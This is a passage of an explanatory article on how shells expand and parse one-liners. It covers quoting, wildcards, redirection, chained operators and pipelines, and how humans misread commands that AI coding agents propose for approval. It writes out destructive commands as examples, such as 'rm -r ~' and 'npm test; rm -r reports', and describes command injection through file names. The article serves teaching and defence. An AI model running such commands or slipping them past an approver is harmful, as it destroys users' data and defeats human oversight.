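# How accurately programmers read shell one-liners, pipelines and quoting

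## What does the shell do to a line before running it?

A shell is a program that reads lines of text as commands and starts the programs they name. Bash, sh and zsh are common shells on Linux and Mac computers. People usually use a shell through a terminal, a window where they type commands and see the output. Programmers use shells to install software, move and delete files, search logs and run tests. Many of these jobs fit on a single line (a "one-liner"), even when they require several programs that pass data to each other.

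Reading a one-liner accurately means predicting what it will do to the computer. Experienced programmers can get this wrong because the shell changes the line before running it. It replaces parts of the text with other text, such as a stored value or a list of file names, and passes only the result to the programs. This replacement is called expansion. GNU's *What is a shell?*, part of the Bash manual, calls a shell "simply a macro processor that executes commands". A macro processor is a program that expands short pieces of text into longer ones. Ramey, who maintains Bash, similarly describes in *The Bourne-Again Shell* how a line passes through a series of stages, changing at each one, until the shell executes a command. POSIX, the standard for Unix-like systems (The Open Group, 2024), sets the order of those stages. Individual shells mostly follow it and add their own features.

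### The parts of a line

The simplest line is one command, which is the name of a program followed by its arguments, the pieces of text that tell the program what to work on. In `ls -l reports`, the program `ls` lists files, and `-l` and `reports` are its arguments. By convention, an argument that starts with a hyphen is an option, a setting that changes how the program behaves (`-l` produces a more detailed list). The shell passes options along as ordinary text, and the program interprets them.

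A variable is text stored under a name. The line `dir=reports` stores the text `reports` under the name `dir`, and a later `$dir` or `${dir}` stands for whatever the variable holds at that moment.

Most programs print their results to a channel called standard output and can read from another called standard input. A pipe, written `|`, connects the output of one program to the input of the next, and commands joined this way form a pipeline. Redirection connects a program to a file instead. The operator `>` sends output to a file, emptying the file first if it exists, `>>` adds to the end of the file, and `<` takes input from a file.

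When a program ends, it returns a number called its exit status. Zero means success, and any other number usually means failure, although some programs use other numbers for ordinary outcomes. For example, `grep`, which searches files for a piece of text, returns 1 when it finds nothing. Three operators chain commands. The command after `;` runs regardless of the exit status so far, the command after `&&` runs only if that status is zero, and the command after `||` runs only if it is not zero. In many programming languages `&&` has higher precedence than `||`, but in the shell they have equal precedence and the shell evaluates them from left to right. The Open Group gives the example `true || echo foo && echo bar`, which prints `bar` (`true` does nothing except succeed, and `echo` prints its arguments). A programmer who applied the rule from C or Java would expect the line to print nothing.

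### The order of processing

The shell takes a line through these steps:

1. Parsing. The shell cuts the line into words and operators, at unquoted spaces and at characters such as `;`, `|` and `>`, and groups the words into commands.
2. Tilde, variable, command and arithmetic expansion, in one pass from left to right. A leading `~` becomes the path of the user's home directory, `$x` becomes the value of the variable `x`, `$(date)` becomes whatever the program `date` prints, and `$((2+3))` becomes `5`.
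3. Word splitting. Where an unquoted variable, command or arithmetic expansion produced text containing spaces, tabs or newlines, the shell cuts that text into separate words.
4. Globbing. The shell replaces a word containing an unquoted wildcard with the names of the files that match it, in sorted order. The wildcard `*` stands for any run of characters and `?` for any single one. If no file matches, the pattern stays as it is.
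5. Quote removal. The shell deletes the quotation marks and backslashes that governed the earlier steps.
6. Redirection. The shell opens the files that `>`, `>>` and `<` name, and leaves the operators and file names out of the program's arguments.
7. Execution. The shell looks for the command name among its own functions and built-in commands, then in the directories that the variable `PATH` lists, and starts what it finds.

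What the program receives at the last step is its argument list: the exact strings left once the expansions are over.

The shell parses a line before expanding variables, so it treats an operator inside a variable's value as ordinary text. If `x` holds the text `a; b`, then `echo $x` prints `a; b` and the shell does not try to run a program called `b`. During expansion, the shell also does not go back over what it has produced. Greenberg and Blatt (2019), in *Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell*, set `usr` to `root` and run `echo ~$usr`. The output is `~root`, although the shell would have expanded `~root` to the path of root's home directory if it had been typed directly.

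Unlike the other expansions, command expansion runs a program to get the replacement text. A line that begins with a harmless command like `echo` can therefore run another program, with its own side effects, before `echo` runs.

The shell also expands each command only when it is about to run it. In `cd build && ls *`, the first command moves into the directory `build`, and the asterisk then matches the files there. If the move fails, the shell never expands the asterisk.

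The timing of word splitting matters most for counting arguments. According to GNU's *Word Splitting*, the shell splits only the results of expansions. Globbing comes after splitting, so a matching file whose name contains a space is still passed as one argument. *The Bash Parser*, a tutorial on Greg's Wiki, gives a different order, with quote removal near the start and word splitting after file-name expansion. Taken literally, that order would split the name `old api.log` in two whenever a wildcard matched it, which does not happen.

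Bash adds brace expansion before the other steps, turning `{a,b}` into `a b`. According to GNU's *Shell Expansions*, only brace expansion, word splitting and globbing can turn one word into several, apart from a few special forms such as `"$@"`, which stands for all of a script's arguments. By default, zsh does not split unquoted variables, so a line can behave differently on a Mac, where zsh is the standard shell, than in Bash on a server.

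### What quotes switch off

Quotation marks in the shell control which of the steps above apply to the characters between them, whereas in most programming languages they show where a piece of text begins and ends.

| Step | No quotes | Double quotes | Single quotes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Treating `;`, `>` and similar characters as operators | on | off | off |
| Tilde expansion | on | off | off |
| Variable, command and arithmetic expansion | on | on | off |
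| Word splitting of the results | on | off | off |
| Globbing | on | off | off |

Single quotes remove the special meaning of every character between them, and the only character they cannot contain is another single quote. Inside double quotes, only the dollar sign, the backslash and the backquote (an older way of writing command expansion) keep a special meaning. Outside quotes, a backslash removes the special meaning of the next character or, at the end of a line, joins that line to the next. Inside double quotes, it does this only before a dollar sign, a backquote, a double quote, another backslash or a line break, and is an ordinary character before anything else.

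Allen's course notes, *Shell Command Line Quoting Mechanisms* (2019), illustrate the difference between single and double quotes with the variable `SHELL`, which holds the path of the user's shell. The command `echo '$SHELL'` prints the text `$SHELL`, while `echo "$SHELL"` prints `/bin/bash`. In `echo "'$SHELL'"`, the shell still expands the variable because the outer quotes are double and the single quotes inside them are plain characters.

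The shell starts a new argument at an unquoted space, not at a quote, so `My" "Documents` and `'My Documents'` both produce the single argument `My Documents`, and the program can't detect which form someone typed.

### One line through every stage

Suppose that a user called ana wants to collect every log line that mentions a timeout. The variable `dir` holds `/srv/web logs`, a directory whose name contains a space. In it are three files: `api.log`, `old api.log` and `notes.txt`. The user types:

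```
grep -h timeout "$dir"/*.log | sort > ~/timeouts.txt
```

The `-h` option keeps `grep` from printing the file name before each matching line, and `sort` puts lines in order.

The shell parses the line into two commands with a pipe between them. The first consists of the words `grep`, `-h`, `timeout` and `"$dir"/*.log`. The last of these is a single word because it contains no unquoted space. The second command consists of `sort` and a redirection to `~/timeouts.txt`. The shell connects the first command's output to the second's input before it performs any redirection.

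The first command contains no tilde to expand, and the line contains no command or arithmetic expansion, so the shell replaces only the variable at this stage. `$dir` becomes `/srv/web logs`, and the double quotes around it prevent word splitting at the space. The asterisk is outside the quotes, so the shell does apply globbing and finds two names in `/srv/web logs` that end in `.log`. It then removes the quotation marks.

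For the second command, the shell expands the tilde in the redirection to get `/home/ana/timeouts.txt`, then opens that file, emptying it if it already exists. The shell expands the target of a redirection much as it expands arguments, but Bash reports an error if the target expands to more than one word, according to the GNU Bash manual.

The two programs then start with these argument lists:

| | First program | Second program |
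|---|---|---|
| Command name | `grep` | `sort` |
| Argument 1 | `-h` | none |
| Argument 2 | `timeout` | |
| Argument 3 | `/srv/web logs/api.log` | |
| Argument 4 | `/srv/web logs/old api.log` | |

No dollar sign, asterisk, quotation mark or pipe remains by the time the commands run. `grep` receives two complete file names, just as if the user had typed them. `sort` receives no arguments; it reads from its input and writes to its output, which the shell has already connected to the file.

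Unless the `pipefail` option is set, a pipeline returns the exit status of its last command. If neither log mentions a timeout, `grep` returns 1 but `sort` receives no input and returns 0, so the whole line counts as a success even though any earlier contents of `timeouts.txt` are gone.

Without the two quotation marks, the argument list changes. The shell splits the value of `dir` into words, producing `/srv/web` and `logs/*.log`. The first has no wildcard, so it stays the same. The second is a pattern for files in a directory called `logs` inside the current directory. If that directory doesn't exist, `grep` reports that neither `/srv/web` nor `logs/*.log` exists. If it does, `grep` reports only `/srv/web` as missing and searches the wrong logs.

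### Why the shell works this way

A language designed today would probably keep a file name in one piece wherever a program passed it, but Greenberg (2018), in *Word Expansion Supports POSIX Shell Interactivity*, argues that the shell's expansion suits people who type a command, look at the result and type the next one. They need short commands and often want to handle a group of files together. The line `mv *.c code/` moves every file whose name ends in `.c` into the directory `code`. It works because the shell expands the pattern into a list and `mv` accepts any number of files. Greenberg compares this with the same task in scsh, a shell built on the programming language Scheme, where the usual solution is a loop that finds the matching files and builds a new name for each. scsh also allows a shorter version, but the user still has to ask for the file matching explicitly and mark where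 the resulting list goes.

Greenberg calls this a conjecture, and the data behind it come from three sessions of Greenberg's own shell history. Of the 1,155 commands, about four in five took at least one argument, and about one in ten used a program's ability to accept a varying number of arguments. This shows that the feature gets used, but it is little evidence of how other people work. The argument is also stronger for globbing than for word splitting. Moving the `.c` files doesn't require splitting a value, and Greenberg considers the default of splitting at spaces a critical weakness, which small changes to the shell might fix without breaking most existing scripts.

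The argument also depends on feedback. Before running a command that changes files, Greenberg often puts `echo` in front of it, so the shell does the expansions and prints the resulting command. This catches many surprises, but `echo` separates its arguments with single spaces, so the output doesn't show where one argument ends and the next begins. Someone working at a terminal also knows which directory they are in, has usually just looked at the files, and can try a line out before committing to it. Someone approving a line written by a machine may have none of these advantages.

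### Approving a command that an agent proposes

An AI coding agent uses a language model to carry out programming tasks by editing files and running shell commands on the user's computer. Many agents can ask for permission before running a command. Anthropic's documentation for its agent Claude Code shows a typical prompt, with a short description ("Run the test suite"), the command `npm test`, and the question "Do you want to proceed?" The user can approve once, approve and not be asked again for commands of that form, switch to a mode in which a classifier reviews actions instead, or refuse. How often such prompts appear depends on the settings. Claude Code runs many read-only commands without asking. OpenAI's agent Codex has two separate controls, a sandbox that limits what a command can do and an approval policy that determines when the agent must ask. In the Claude Code example, the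 user sees the command as the agent wrote it, and the shell performs its expansions only after the user approves.

An approver can go wrong here in three ways, which call for different remedies.

Inattention is approving a command without reading it closely. Suppose a user has approved `npm test` a dozen times in an afternoon, and the next prompt contains `npm test; rm -r reports`. The `rm -r` command deletes the `reports` directory and everything in it. Anyone who read to the end of the line would notice this, but the user recognises the beginning, or glances at the description, and approves the command.

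Misparse is reading a command closely and still getting wrong what the shell will do with it. In an example from Greenberg, a directory contains three files, `file1`, `file2` and `file1 file2`, and the variable `x` holds the text `file1 file2`. A careful reader who knows all this expects `rm ${x}` to delete the third file. The shell instead splits the value at the space and passes two arguments to `rm`, which deletes the first two files and leaves the third. The reader didn't know the splitting rule, so neither more care nor more information about the directory would have helped. Greenberg and Blatt attribute a well-known accident, in which a script from the games platform Steam deleted users' files, to a misunderstanding of expansion.

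A command has missing state when its text leaves out facts that determine its effect. For example, `npm test` contains nothing for the shell to expand and nothing to misread, but `npm`, a tool for managing JavaScript projects, runs whatever command the project's configuration file lists under the name "test". That command might run a test suite or empty a database, and even a reader who knows shell syntax well cannot tell which from the text alone. The value of a variable, the contents of a script and the files in a directory can also be missing from a command's text.

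A single line can involve both a misparse and missing state. Claude Code normally runs `find`, a program that searches directories, without a prompt, but in its Manual mode it asks first if the command contains an unquoted wildcard. It asks because, according to Anthropic, the wildcard could expand to an option such as `-delete`, which makes `find` delete the files it finds. This can happen if the directory contains a file with that name, since the shell treats options and file names alike. An approver who does not know this has misparsed the line, and even one who does has to look in the directory to tell whether it will happen.

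## Which parts of a shell line are easiest to misread?

Many of the examples below come from *Bash Pitfalls*, a large collection of shell mistakes on Greg's Wiki. Most of its 65 numbered entries give a faulty line, explain the problem and offer a correction. Other examples come from the POSIX standard, teaching material and messages to the Bash mailing lists. These sources show that the mistakes are possible and, in a few cases, that a particular person made one. They don't measure how often readers make them, since nobody counts the times someone read the same line correctly. They also mostly concern people writing commands, who discover a mistake when the result looks wrong, whereas someone approving a command has to spot it before the command runs.

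### Variables and quotes

The line `cp $file $target` looks like it copies one file to one place, and it does if neither value contains a space or a wildcard. If `file` holds `old api.log`, the shell splits the value at the space, and `cp` tries to copy two files, `old` and `api.log`. The correct form is `cp -- "$file" "$target"`, where `--` marks the end of the options.

The shell also expands wildcards in the value of an unquoted variable. In an example from *Bash Pitfalls*, the variable `msg` holds the text `Please enter a file name of the form *.zip`. The command `echo $msg` prints that sentence with `*.zip` replaced by the names of the zip files in the current directory. This can mislead a programmer who is using `echo` to check a variable, because the variable itself hasn't changed. `echo "$msg"` prints the sentence as stored.

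An empty value disappears from a command if the variable is unquoted. For example, `[ -n $name ]` looks like a test that `name` is not empty, but it also succeeds when `name` is empty. The opening bracket is a command, and `-n`, the value and the closing bracket are its arguments. If `name` is empty, the only argument before the closing bracket is `-n`. With one argument there, the command only checks that the argument contains some text, and `-n` does. `[ -n "$name" ]` keeps the empty value as an argument, so the test fails as it should.

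Variables don't always need quotes. According to *Bash bugs*, a set of teaching slides, the shell doesn't split or glob the value in an assignment such as `copy=$file`. Bash's double-bracket test, `[[ -n $name ]]`, is also safe without quotes. A reader therefore has to notice missing quotes and know where splitting happens.

The command `dir=/tmp/old ls $dir` can look as if it sets `dir` and then lists that directory, but under The Open Group's rules, the shell expands a command's arguments before it carries out an assignment at the front of the same command. `$dir` therefore still has its earlier value. If it had none, `ls` receives no argument and lists the current directory. In `dir=/tmp/old; ls "$dir"`, the semicolon makes the assignment happen first.

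**Quotation marks inside a value.** Suppose a script stores some options with `ARGS='--arg "1 2 3"'` and later runs a program with `$ARGS`. The natural expectation is that the program receives two arguments, `--arg` and `1 2 3`. But the shell removes only the quotation marks that were in the line as someone typed it, and those that arrive from a variable are ordinary characters. *When Quoting Variables Backfires*, a programmer's blog post, tests the alternatives with a small program that prints its arguments:

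| How the line passes the options | What the program receives |
|---|---|
| `$ARGS` | four arguments: `--arg`, `"1`, `2` and `3"` |
| `"$ARGS"` | one argument: `--arg "1 2 3"` |
| `"${ARGS[@]}"`, after `ARGS=(--arg "1 2 3")` | two arguments: `--arg` and `1 2 3` |

The last row uses an array, a variable that holds a list of separate values. The post's author had expected the first form to produce two arguments, and discovered the problem after moving a working command into an automated job on GitHub. The job stored the options in a variable with their quotation marks, and a cloud storage tool rejected an address that now began and ended with a quotation mark. Deleting the marks from the variable fixed the problem, but this works only if no option contains a space.

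**Single and double quotes.** The command `sed 's/$foo/good bye/'` uses the text-editing program `sed` to replace the literal characters `$foo` with `good bye`, because the shell doesn't expand variables inside single quotes. It is easy to misread as replacing the value of `foo`. With double quotes, `sed "s/$foo/good bye/"` does use the value, though a slash in the value would end the search pattern early.

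Double quotes also prevent tilde expansion, which readers may expect to still work. `mkdir -p "~/backup"` makes a directory named `~` in the current directory, with `backup` inside it, although it appears to make `backup` in the user's home directory. Running `rm -r ~` to clean up would then delete the user's real home directory. `"$HOME/backup"` and `~/"backup"` both give the intended path.

Nested quotes can make a correct line look wrong. According to *Bash Pitfalls*, a C programmer reading `cd "$(dirname "$f")"` would pair the first quotation mark with the second and the third with the fourth, leaving `$f` unquoted. The shell parses the quotes inside `$(...)` separately from those outside, so both the variable and the command's output are quoted.

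Some commands pass text to a second shell. `ssh` runs a command on another computer, and `bash -c` starts a new copy of Bash to run the text that follows. The outer quotes determine which of the two shells expands a variable.

In `ssh server "du -sh $HOME"`, where `du` measures disk use, the double quotes let the user's own shell replace `$HOME` before `ssh` starts. The server then receives a path from the user's laptop, which may not exist on the server, even though the command reads like a request for the size of the home directory there. With `ssh server 'du -sh "$HOME"'`, the server's shell does the expansion.

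A second shell can also parse a variable's value as shell syntax, which the first shell does not do. If `x` holds `a; b`, then `echo $x` just prints `a; b`, but `bash -c "echo $x"` gives the new shell the text `echo a; b`, so it prints `a` and then tries to run a program called `b`. The safe form keeps the program text fixed and passes the value as an argument: `bash -c 'echo "$1"' bash "$x"`. File names can cause the same problem. In `find . -exec sh -c 'echo {}' \;`, GNU `find` inserts each file name into the text that `sh` parses, so a file name containing `$(...)` can run a command.

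Two shells parse a command sent through `ssh`, and the second needs its own quotes. `ssh server rm 'old api.log'` looks properly quoted, but the local shell removes the quotation marks and `ssh` joins the arguments with spaces. The server's shell then splits the name at the space and deletes `old` and `api.log`, if they exist. Writing `ssh server "rm 'old api.log'"` preserves the inner quotes for the server's shell.

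### Wildcards

A pattern that matches no file normally stays in the line as text, which means that a faulty command can work by accident. One of the debugging exercises in *The Unix Shell* uses this line, which is supposed to find every CSV file under the directory `data`:

```
find data -name *.csv
```

In `find data -name *.csv`, `find` receives the pattern, as a reader would naturally assume, only if the current directory contains no CSV files. If the only CSV file there is `totals.csv`, the shell replaces the pattern with that name, and `find` looks under `data` only for files called `totals.csv`. If there are two CSV files, `find` receives an extra argument and reports an error. Quoting the pattern, as in `find data -name '*.csv'`, always passes it to `find` unchanged.

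The same rule affects loops. `for f in *.mp3` runs the loop once for each matching file, but if no files match, it still runs once, with `f` set to the text `*.mp3`. A script can guard against this by checking that the file exists before using it. By default, zsh reports an error when a pattern matches nothing, so the same line may fail on a Mac, where zsh is the default shell, but run in Bash.

It is also easy to misread which permissions apply to a wildcard. `sudo` runs a command with administrator rights, so `sudo ls /foo/*` seems to list everything in a protected directory, but the user's own shell expands the wildcard before `sudo` starts. If that shell does not have permission to read `/foo`, The Open Group's rules require it to continue as though no files matched. `ls` then looks, with administrator rights, for a file whose name is an asterisk. The correct form, `sudo sh -c 'ls /foo/*'`,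 starts a shell that has the rights to expand the pattern.

**File names that look like options.** `rm *` can delete subdirectories as well as ordinary files, which is easy to miss because `rm` normally refuses to delete directories without an option such as `-r`. If one of the files is called `-r`, `rm` treats its name as an option, deletes the subdirectories too, and leaves that file in place. A hyphen sorts before letters in most language settings, so such a name usually comes early in the list of names that replaces `*`.

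There are two common remedies. The `--` in `rm -- *` marks the end of the options, but not every program recognises it. `rm ./*` makes every name begin with `./`, so none can begin with a hyphen.

**Wildcards.** In the shell, `*` skips hidden files, whose names begin with a dot, though many people read it as "everything". `rm -rf build/*` therefore leaves `build/.cache` in place. `find` uses similar patterns without that exception, so `find build -name '*'` does include it. Depending on the computer's language settings, `[a-z]` may also match accented letters.

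Differences of this kind are the subject of Lim, Adkins and Marron (2026), in *An Empirical Analysis of the Glob Ecosystem*. They extracted 62,713 patterns from 1,966 open-source projects in Bash, Python, Node.js (which runs JavaScript outside a browser), Ruby, PHP and Go. They also examined 2,160 GitHub issues, Stack Overflow questions and security reports about wildcards. About 91% of the patterns used `*`, which every tool supports. The trouble was mostly with the details:

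- Hidden files. Python's `glob.glob` leaves them out by default, while `pathlib.Path.glob`, also part of Python, includes them.
- Searching subdirectories. Many tools use `**` to mean "at any depth", but Python's `glob.glob` does so only with an extra setting. Bash also needs an option, `globstar`. Without it, `rm **/*.log` deletes log files exactly one level down, whereas zsh searches every level by default.
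- Upper and lower case. In one question from Stack Overflow, `*.txt` matched a file ending in `.TXT` on Windows but not on Linux, and the user's program broke.
- Letter ranges. In another post, `rm [a-z]*` deleted files on a production system that it had left alone during development.

Lim and colleagues counted 40 posts about patterns that worked in one tool and failed in another, and 49 about differences between platforms. Because they searched for posts about problems, these counts don't show how often a pattern goes wrong. Only about 8% of the patterns came from shell projects, and 91% of all patterns were in configuration files. The paper's table of features also needs some care, since it wrongly lists Bash as lacking brace expansion. Even so, the examples show how someone who learned wildcards in Python or Node.js could confidently misread a shell pattern.

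### Redirection

Programs have a separate channel for error messages, called standard error. The shell numbers it 2, and numbers standard output 1. The redirection `2>&1` sends errors to wherever standard output is going at that moment. `cmd > log 2>&1` and `cmd 2>&1 > log` therefore do different things, although both can be read as "send output and errors to the log". The shell handles redirections from left to right:

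| | `cmd > log 2>&1` | `cmd 2>&1 > log` |
|---|---|---|
| At the start | output and errors go to the terminal | output and errors go to the terminal |
| After the first redirection | output goes to `log`, errors to the terminal | no change, since output still goes to the terminal |
| After the second redirection | output and errors go to `log` | output goes to `log`, errors to the terminal |

*Bash Pitfalls* calls the second version "by far the most common mistake involving redirections", but gives no count. That order can also be deliberate, as in `cmd 2>&1 > log | less`. The shell connects the pipe before it handles the redirections, so the errors go through the pipe to `less`, which shows them a page at a time, and the normal output goes to `log`.

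The order of operations is also easy to misread. The shell opens an output file for writing, which empties it, before starting the command. `sort f > f` therefore erases the contents of `f`, although it looks as if it sorts the file and saves the result under the same name. *Bash bugs* demonstrates this with `wc`, which counts lines, words and characters. `wc < foo` printed 11, 92 and 544, but after `wc < foo > foo` the file contained three zeros. `sort -o f f` safely saves the sorted result to the same file. With other programs, the usual solution is a temporary file, as in `sed 's/foo/bar/' f > tmp && mv tmp f`.

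A pipeline makes the result less predictable. In `cat f | sed 's/foo/bar/' > f`, the two commands start at about the same time, so `cat` may read some or all of the file before the shell empties it. The line can occasionally work, particularly on a small file, but according to *Bash Pitfalls* it can also leave the file empty or cut short, or make it grow until the disk is full. The Open Group describes the `noclobber` option, which stops `>` from overwriting an existing file, but a reader can't tell from the line whether it is on.

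The symbol `>` also misleads people who know it as "greater than". In `[ $count > 7 ]`, the shell treats it as a redirection and creates or empties a file called `7`. The `[` command then checks only that `count` isn't empty, so the test succeeds even when `count` is 3. Double brackets prevent the redirection, but `[[ $count > 7 ]]` compares the values as text, so 10 comes before 7. The correct form is `[ "$count" -gt 7 ]`.

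Spacing matters as well. `echo version 2 > notes` writes "version 2" to the file. `echo version 2> notes`, with no space after the digit, prints "version" on the screen and sends any error messages to the file, because a digit directly before `>` is a channel number.

In a loop, the position of the redirection determines how many times the shell empties the file. One exercise in *The Unix Shell* runs `head -n 1 "$f" > summary.txt` inside a loop to collect the first line of each file. Each pass overwrites the previous line, so the summary ends up with only one. Changing `>` to `>>` keeps all the lines, but running the script again adds them a second time. If `> summary.txt` comes after `done`, the word that ends the loop, the shell opens the file only once, which avoids both problems.

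### Chained operators

The following line can delete files that a careful programmer believes are safe:

```
test -d build || mkdir build && rm -rf build/*
```

`test -d build` succeeds if there is a directory called `build`. A programmer applying the precedence rules of C or Java would group the line as `test -d build || { mkdir build && rm -rf build/*; }`. With that grouping, nothing else should run if `build` exists.

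The shell gives `||` and `&&` equal precedence and groups them from the left, so it treats `test -d build || mkdir build && rm -rf build/*` as `{ test -d build || mkdir build; } && rm -rf build/*`. If `build` exists, the test succeeds and the shell skips `mkdir`. It then runs `rm`, because the last command to run before `&&` succeeded.

| Before the line runs | What the shell does | What C's rules predict |
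|---|---|---|
| `build` exists and contains files | skips `mkdir` and deletes the files | skips both `mkdir` and `rm` |
| `build` doesn't exist | creates it, then runs `rm`, which finds nothing | the same |
| `mkdir` can't create `build` | stops after `mkdir` fails | the same |

The two readings differ only in the first case, which is also the only one where files can be lost, so trying the command in a fresh copy of a project would not reveal the mistake. Someone who reads the line as "make sure `build` exists, then empty it" gets the right answer, perhaps without knowing the rule. `mkdir -p build && rm -rf build/*` does the same job more clearly, since `mkdir -p` succeeds if the directory already exists. If the C reading was intended, the line needs explicit braces.

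Fortovey (2024) made this mistake when reporting to the Bash bug list that `printf 1 && printf 2 || printf 3 && printf 4` prints 124 "instead of the expected answer", 12, which C's rules would give. Fortovey soon withdrew the report, calling Bash a strange language with its own logic. Ramey (2024) replied with the grouping written out in braces and added that all Bourne-style shells, which include sh, Bash and zsh, behave this way. Ramey (2017) had already explained the grouping of `true || true && echo hi`, which has the same structure as the `build` example.

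Such chains are easier to read with a method from Wooledge (2022), which goes from left to right and keeps track of the exit status of the last command that ran. In Fortovey's line, `printf 1` succeeds, so `printf 2` runs and also succeeds. The shell then skips `printf 3`, because a command after `||` runs only if there was a failure. The exit status is still zero, so `printf 4` runs after the `&&`. C programmers are likely to misread the line at the skipped command, because they expect the shell to skip everything after `||`.

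Even experts can disagree about how to explain this. When someone on the mailing list described the rule as grouping from the left, Wooledge answered "Not really" and gave the step-by-step method instead. Elz (2022) showed that the two descriptions agree by writing out a seven-command chain with nested braces, and Ramey (2022) confirmed the grouping rule. Wooledge advises against writing such chains at all. Inside Bash's double brackets, however, `&&` has higher precedence than `||`, so a single line can follow both precedence rules.

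In `a && b || c`, `c` runs if either `a` or `b` fails, but many people read the chain as "if a, then b, otherwise c". flyingrhino (2022), in *Possible bug in bash*, reported a script in which the middle part printed "equal" and then tried to list a missing file. The listing failed, so the shell printed a message labelled "SHOULD NOT DISPLAY". Velázquez (2022) replied that this was correct behaviour, because the chain is not equivalent to an `if` statement.

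ShellCheck, a tool that inspects shell scripts for risky patterns without running them, warns about `A && B || C` in *SC2015*. The warning's example is `[[ $dryrun ]] && echo "Would delete file" || rm file`, which seems to print a message during a dry run and delete the file otherwise. If `echo` fails, for instance because something has closed the script's standard output, the shell deletes the file during the dry run. `echo` rarely fails, so this line might work for years, but a test suite or a download in place of `echo` would fail much more often. An ordinary `if ...; then ...; else ...; fi` removes the problem.

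**Semicolons.** `cd /foo; rm -f *` looks as if it deletes files only in `/foo`, but the shell runs `rm` even if `cd` fails. If `/foo` doesn't exist, `rm` deletes the files in the current directory. `cd /foo && rm -f *` runs `rm` only if `cd` succeeds.

A semicolon later in the line can undo this protection. In `cd /srv/app && git pull; rm -rf cache`, a reader may assume that everything depends on the `cd`. According to GNU's *Lists of Commands*, the semicolon has lower precedence than `&&`, so `rm` runs even if the `cd` failed. A missing ampersand is worse. In `cd build & rm -f *`, the single `&` runs `cd` in the background, in a separate copy of the shell. The main shell doesn't wait or change directory, so `rm` deletes the files where the user started.

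*Bash bugs* recommends that scripts use `set -e`, which stops them when a command fails. *Bash Pitfalls* shows why this may not be enough, using a function (a named group of commands) called `cleanup` that changes to a directory and deletes the files in it. With `set -e`, `cleanup /no/longer/there` stops safely when `cd` fails. But if someone later adds an error message by writing `cleanup /no/longer/there || echo failed`, the shell ignores `set -e` inside the function because `||` is checking the function's result. The `cd` fails, and the function deletes files in the wrong directory. Writing `cd -- "$1" || return` inside the function prevents this in both cases.

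Even `cd some/dir && rm -f *` can delete the wrong files. If the variable `CDPATH` lists other places for `cd` to look, `cd` may succeed but enter a different `some/dir`. Writing `cd ./some/dir` prevents this.

### Pipelines

Since a pipeline normally returns the exit status of its last command, an earlier failure can go unnoticed. Suppose that a script backs up a database and then removes the old backups:

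```
mysqldump shop | gzip > shop.sql.gz && rm -r old-backups
```

Here `mysqldump` writes out the contents of the database and `gzip` compresses them. The `&&` seems to mean that the shell will delete the old backups only if the new one works. But if `mysqldump` can't connect to the database, `gzip` receives no input, compresses it without an error and returns zero, so the shell deletes the old backups anyway.

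One solution is to put `set -o pipefail` before the command. The pipeline then returns zero only if all its commands do, and otherwise returns the status of the last one that failed. Another is to avoid the pipe, as in `mysqldump shop > shop.sql && gzip shop.sql && rm -r old-backups`.

With `pipefail` on, the test in `if some_command | grep -q foo` can fail even when `grep` finds `foo`. This happens because `grep -q` stops at the first match, and a program still writing to it may then end with an error. *Bash Pitfalls* recommends turning on `pipefail` only for pipelines where every command after the first reads all of its input.

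Variables can also disappear in a pipeline. The following line seems to count the lines of a file that contain `foo`:

```
count=0; grep foo notes.txt | while read -r line; do count=$((count+1)); done; echo "$count"
```

In Bash, `count=0; grep foo notes.txt | while read -r line; do count=$((count+1)); done; echo "$count"` prints 0, however many lines match. Bash runs each part of a pipeline in a subshell, a separate copy of the shell, and changes to variables there do not reach the original. For a simple count, `grep -c foo notes.txt` is enough. To keep the variable after the loop, a script can supply the input without a pipe: `while read -r line; do ...; done < <(grep foo notes.txt)`. *Bash bugs* describes the same problem with two commands that look interchangeable. `readarray -t names < lines.txt` stores the lines of a file in an array, while `cat lines.txt | readarray -t names` stores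 them in a subshell, where they are lost.

The Open Group's standard allows a shell to run any command in a pipeline in the current shell. ksh93 does this for the last command, and so does Bash when a script turns on the `lastpipe` option. A programmer who learned this behaviour in one shell can therefore misread the same line in another.

### Signs in the text and facts outside it

Some of these lines do the wrong thing whatever the variables and files contain. `[ $count > 7 ]` never compares `count` with 7, and the single quotes in `sed 's/$foo/good bye/'` always stop `$foo` from expanding. A reader who knows the rule needs no other information. In most of the other examples, the text contains a warning sign, but the damage depends on something else:

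| Trap | Sign in the text | What determines the effect |
|---|---|---|
| Unquoted variable | no double quotes around `$x` | spaces, wildcards or an empty value in `x` |
| Unquoted pattern after `find -name` | a bare `*` | matching files in the current directory |
| File name taken as an option | `*` without `./` or `--` before it | a file name that begins with a hyphen |
| Mixed `&&` and `\|\|` | both operators in one chain | which commands succeed |
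| `cd` followed by a semicolon | `;` instead of `&&` | whether the directory exists |
| Hidden pipeline failure | a pipe before `&&` | which command fails, and whether `pipefail` is on |
| Variable lost in a pipeline | an assignment after a pipe | which shell runs the line, and whether `lastpipe` is on |

Errors that occur only with certain variable values are hard to learn about from experience. Someone may run `cp $file $target` hundreds of times with names that contain no spaces, and each success supports the mistaken belief that a variable always stands for one argument. The same line can then fail on the first name that contains a space.

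The safer forms reduce what a reader needs to know. With `rm -- "$f"`, the reader can tell from the text that `rm` receives one file name and no further options, but still has to find out which file that is.

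## What have reading and comprehension experiments found?

Researchers have measured how often people misread C and Python programs by giving many people the same code, asking what it does and marking the answers. The main experiments on shell users instead tested whether people could write a command, which is a related but different skill. Neither group of studies asked experienced programmers what lines of Bash would do.

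### Users who knew the parts but couldn't combine them

In *Expertise in a Computer Operating System*, Doane, Pellegrino and Klatzky (1990) compared people with different amounts of experience using UNIX, the operating system the shell comes from. They studied how these users pictured the system, tested them on understanding and producing commands, and followed their progress over time.

The production test used three kinds of task. Doane, Kintsch and Polson, in *Action Planning*, a 1989 paper that draws on the same data, give an example of each:

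| Kind of task | What the user had to do | Commands needed |
|---|---|---|
| Single | show the names of the files in the current directory | `ls` |
| Multiple | show the file names, sort the contents of file `x`, and show the first ten lines of file `y` | `ls`, `sort x` and `head y` |
| Composite | show the first ten file names in alphabetical order | `ls \| sort \| head` |

Multiple and composite tasks were equally long, but in a composite task each command depended on the one before it. (`ls` normally sorts the names anyway, so `sort` is redundant in this example, although the researchers treated it as part of the answer.)

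On average, the novices had used UNIX for eight months, the intermediates for two years and the experts for five. All had taken a course that taught pipes and redirection and required both in homework. The novices and intermediates could produce the single and multiple commands, but only the experts could produce the composite ones.

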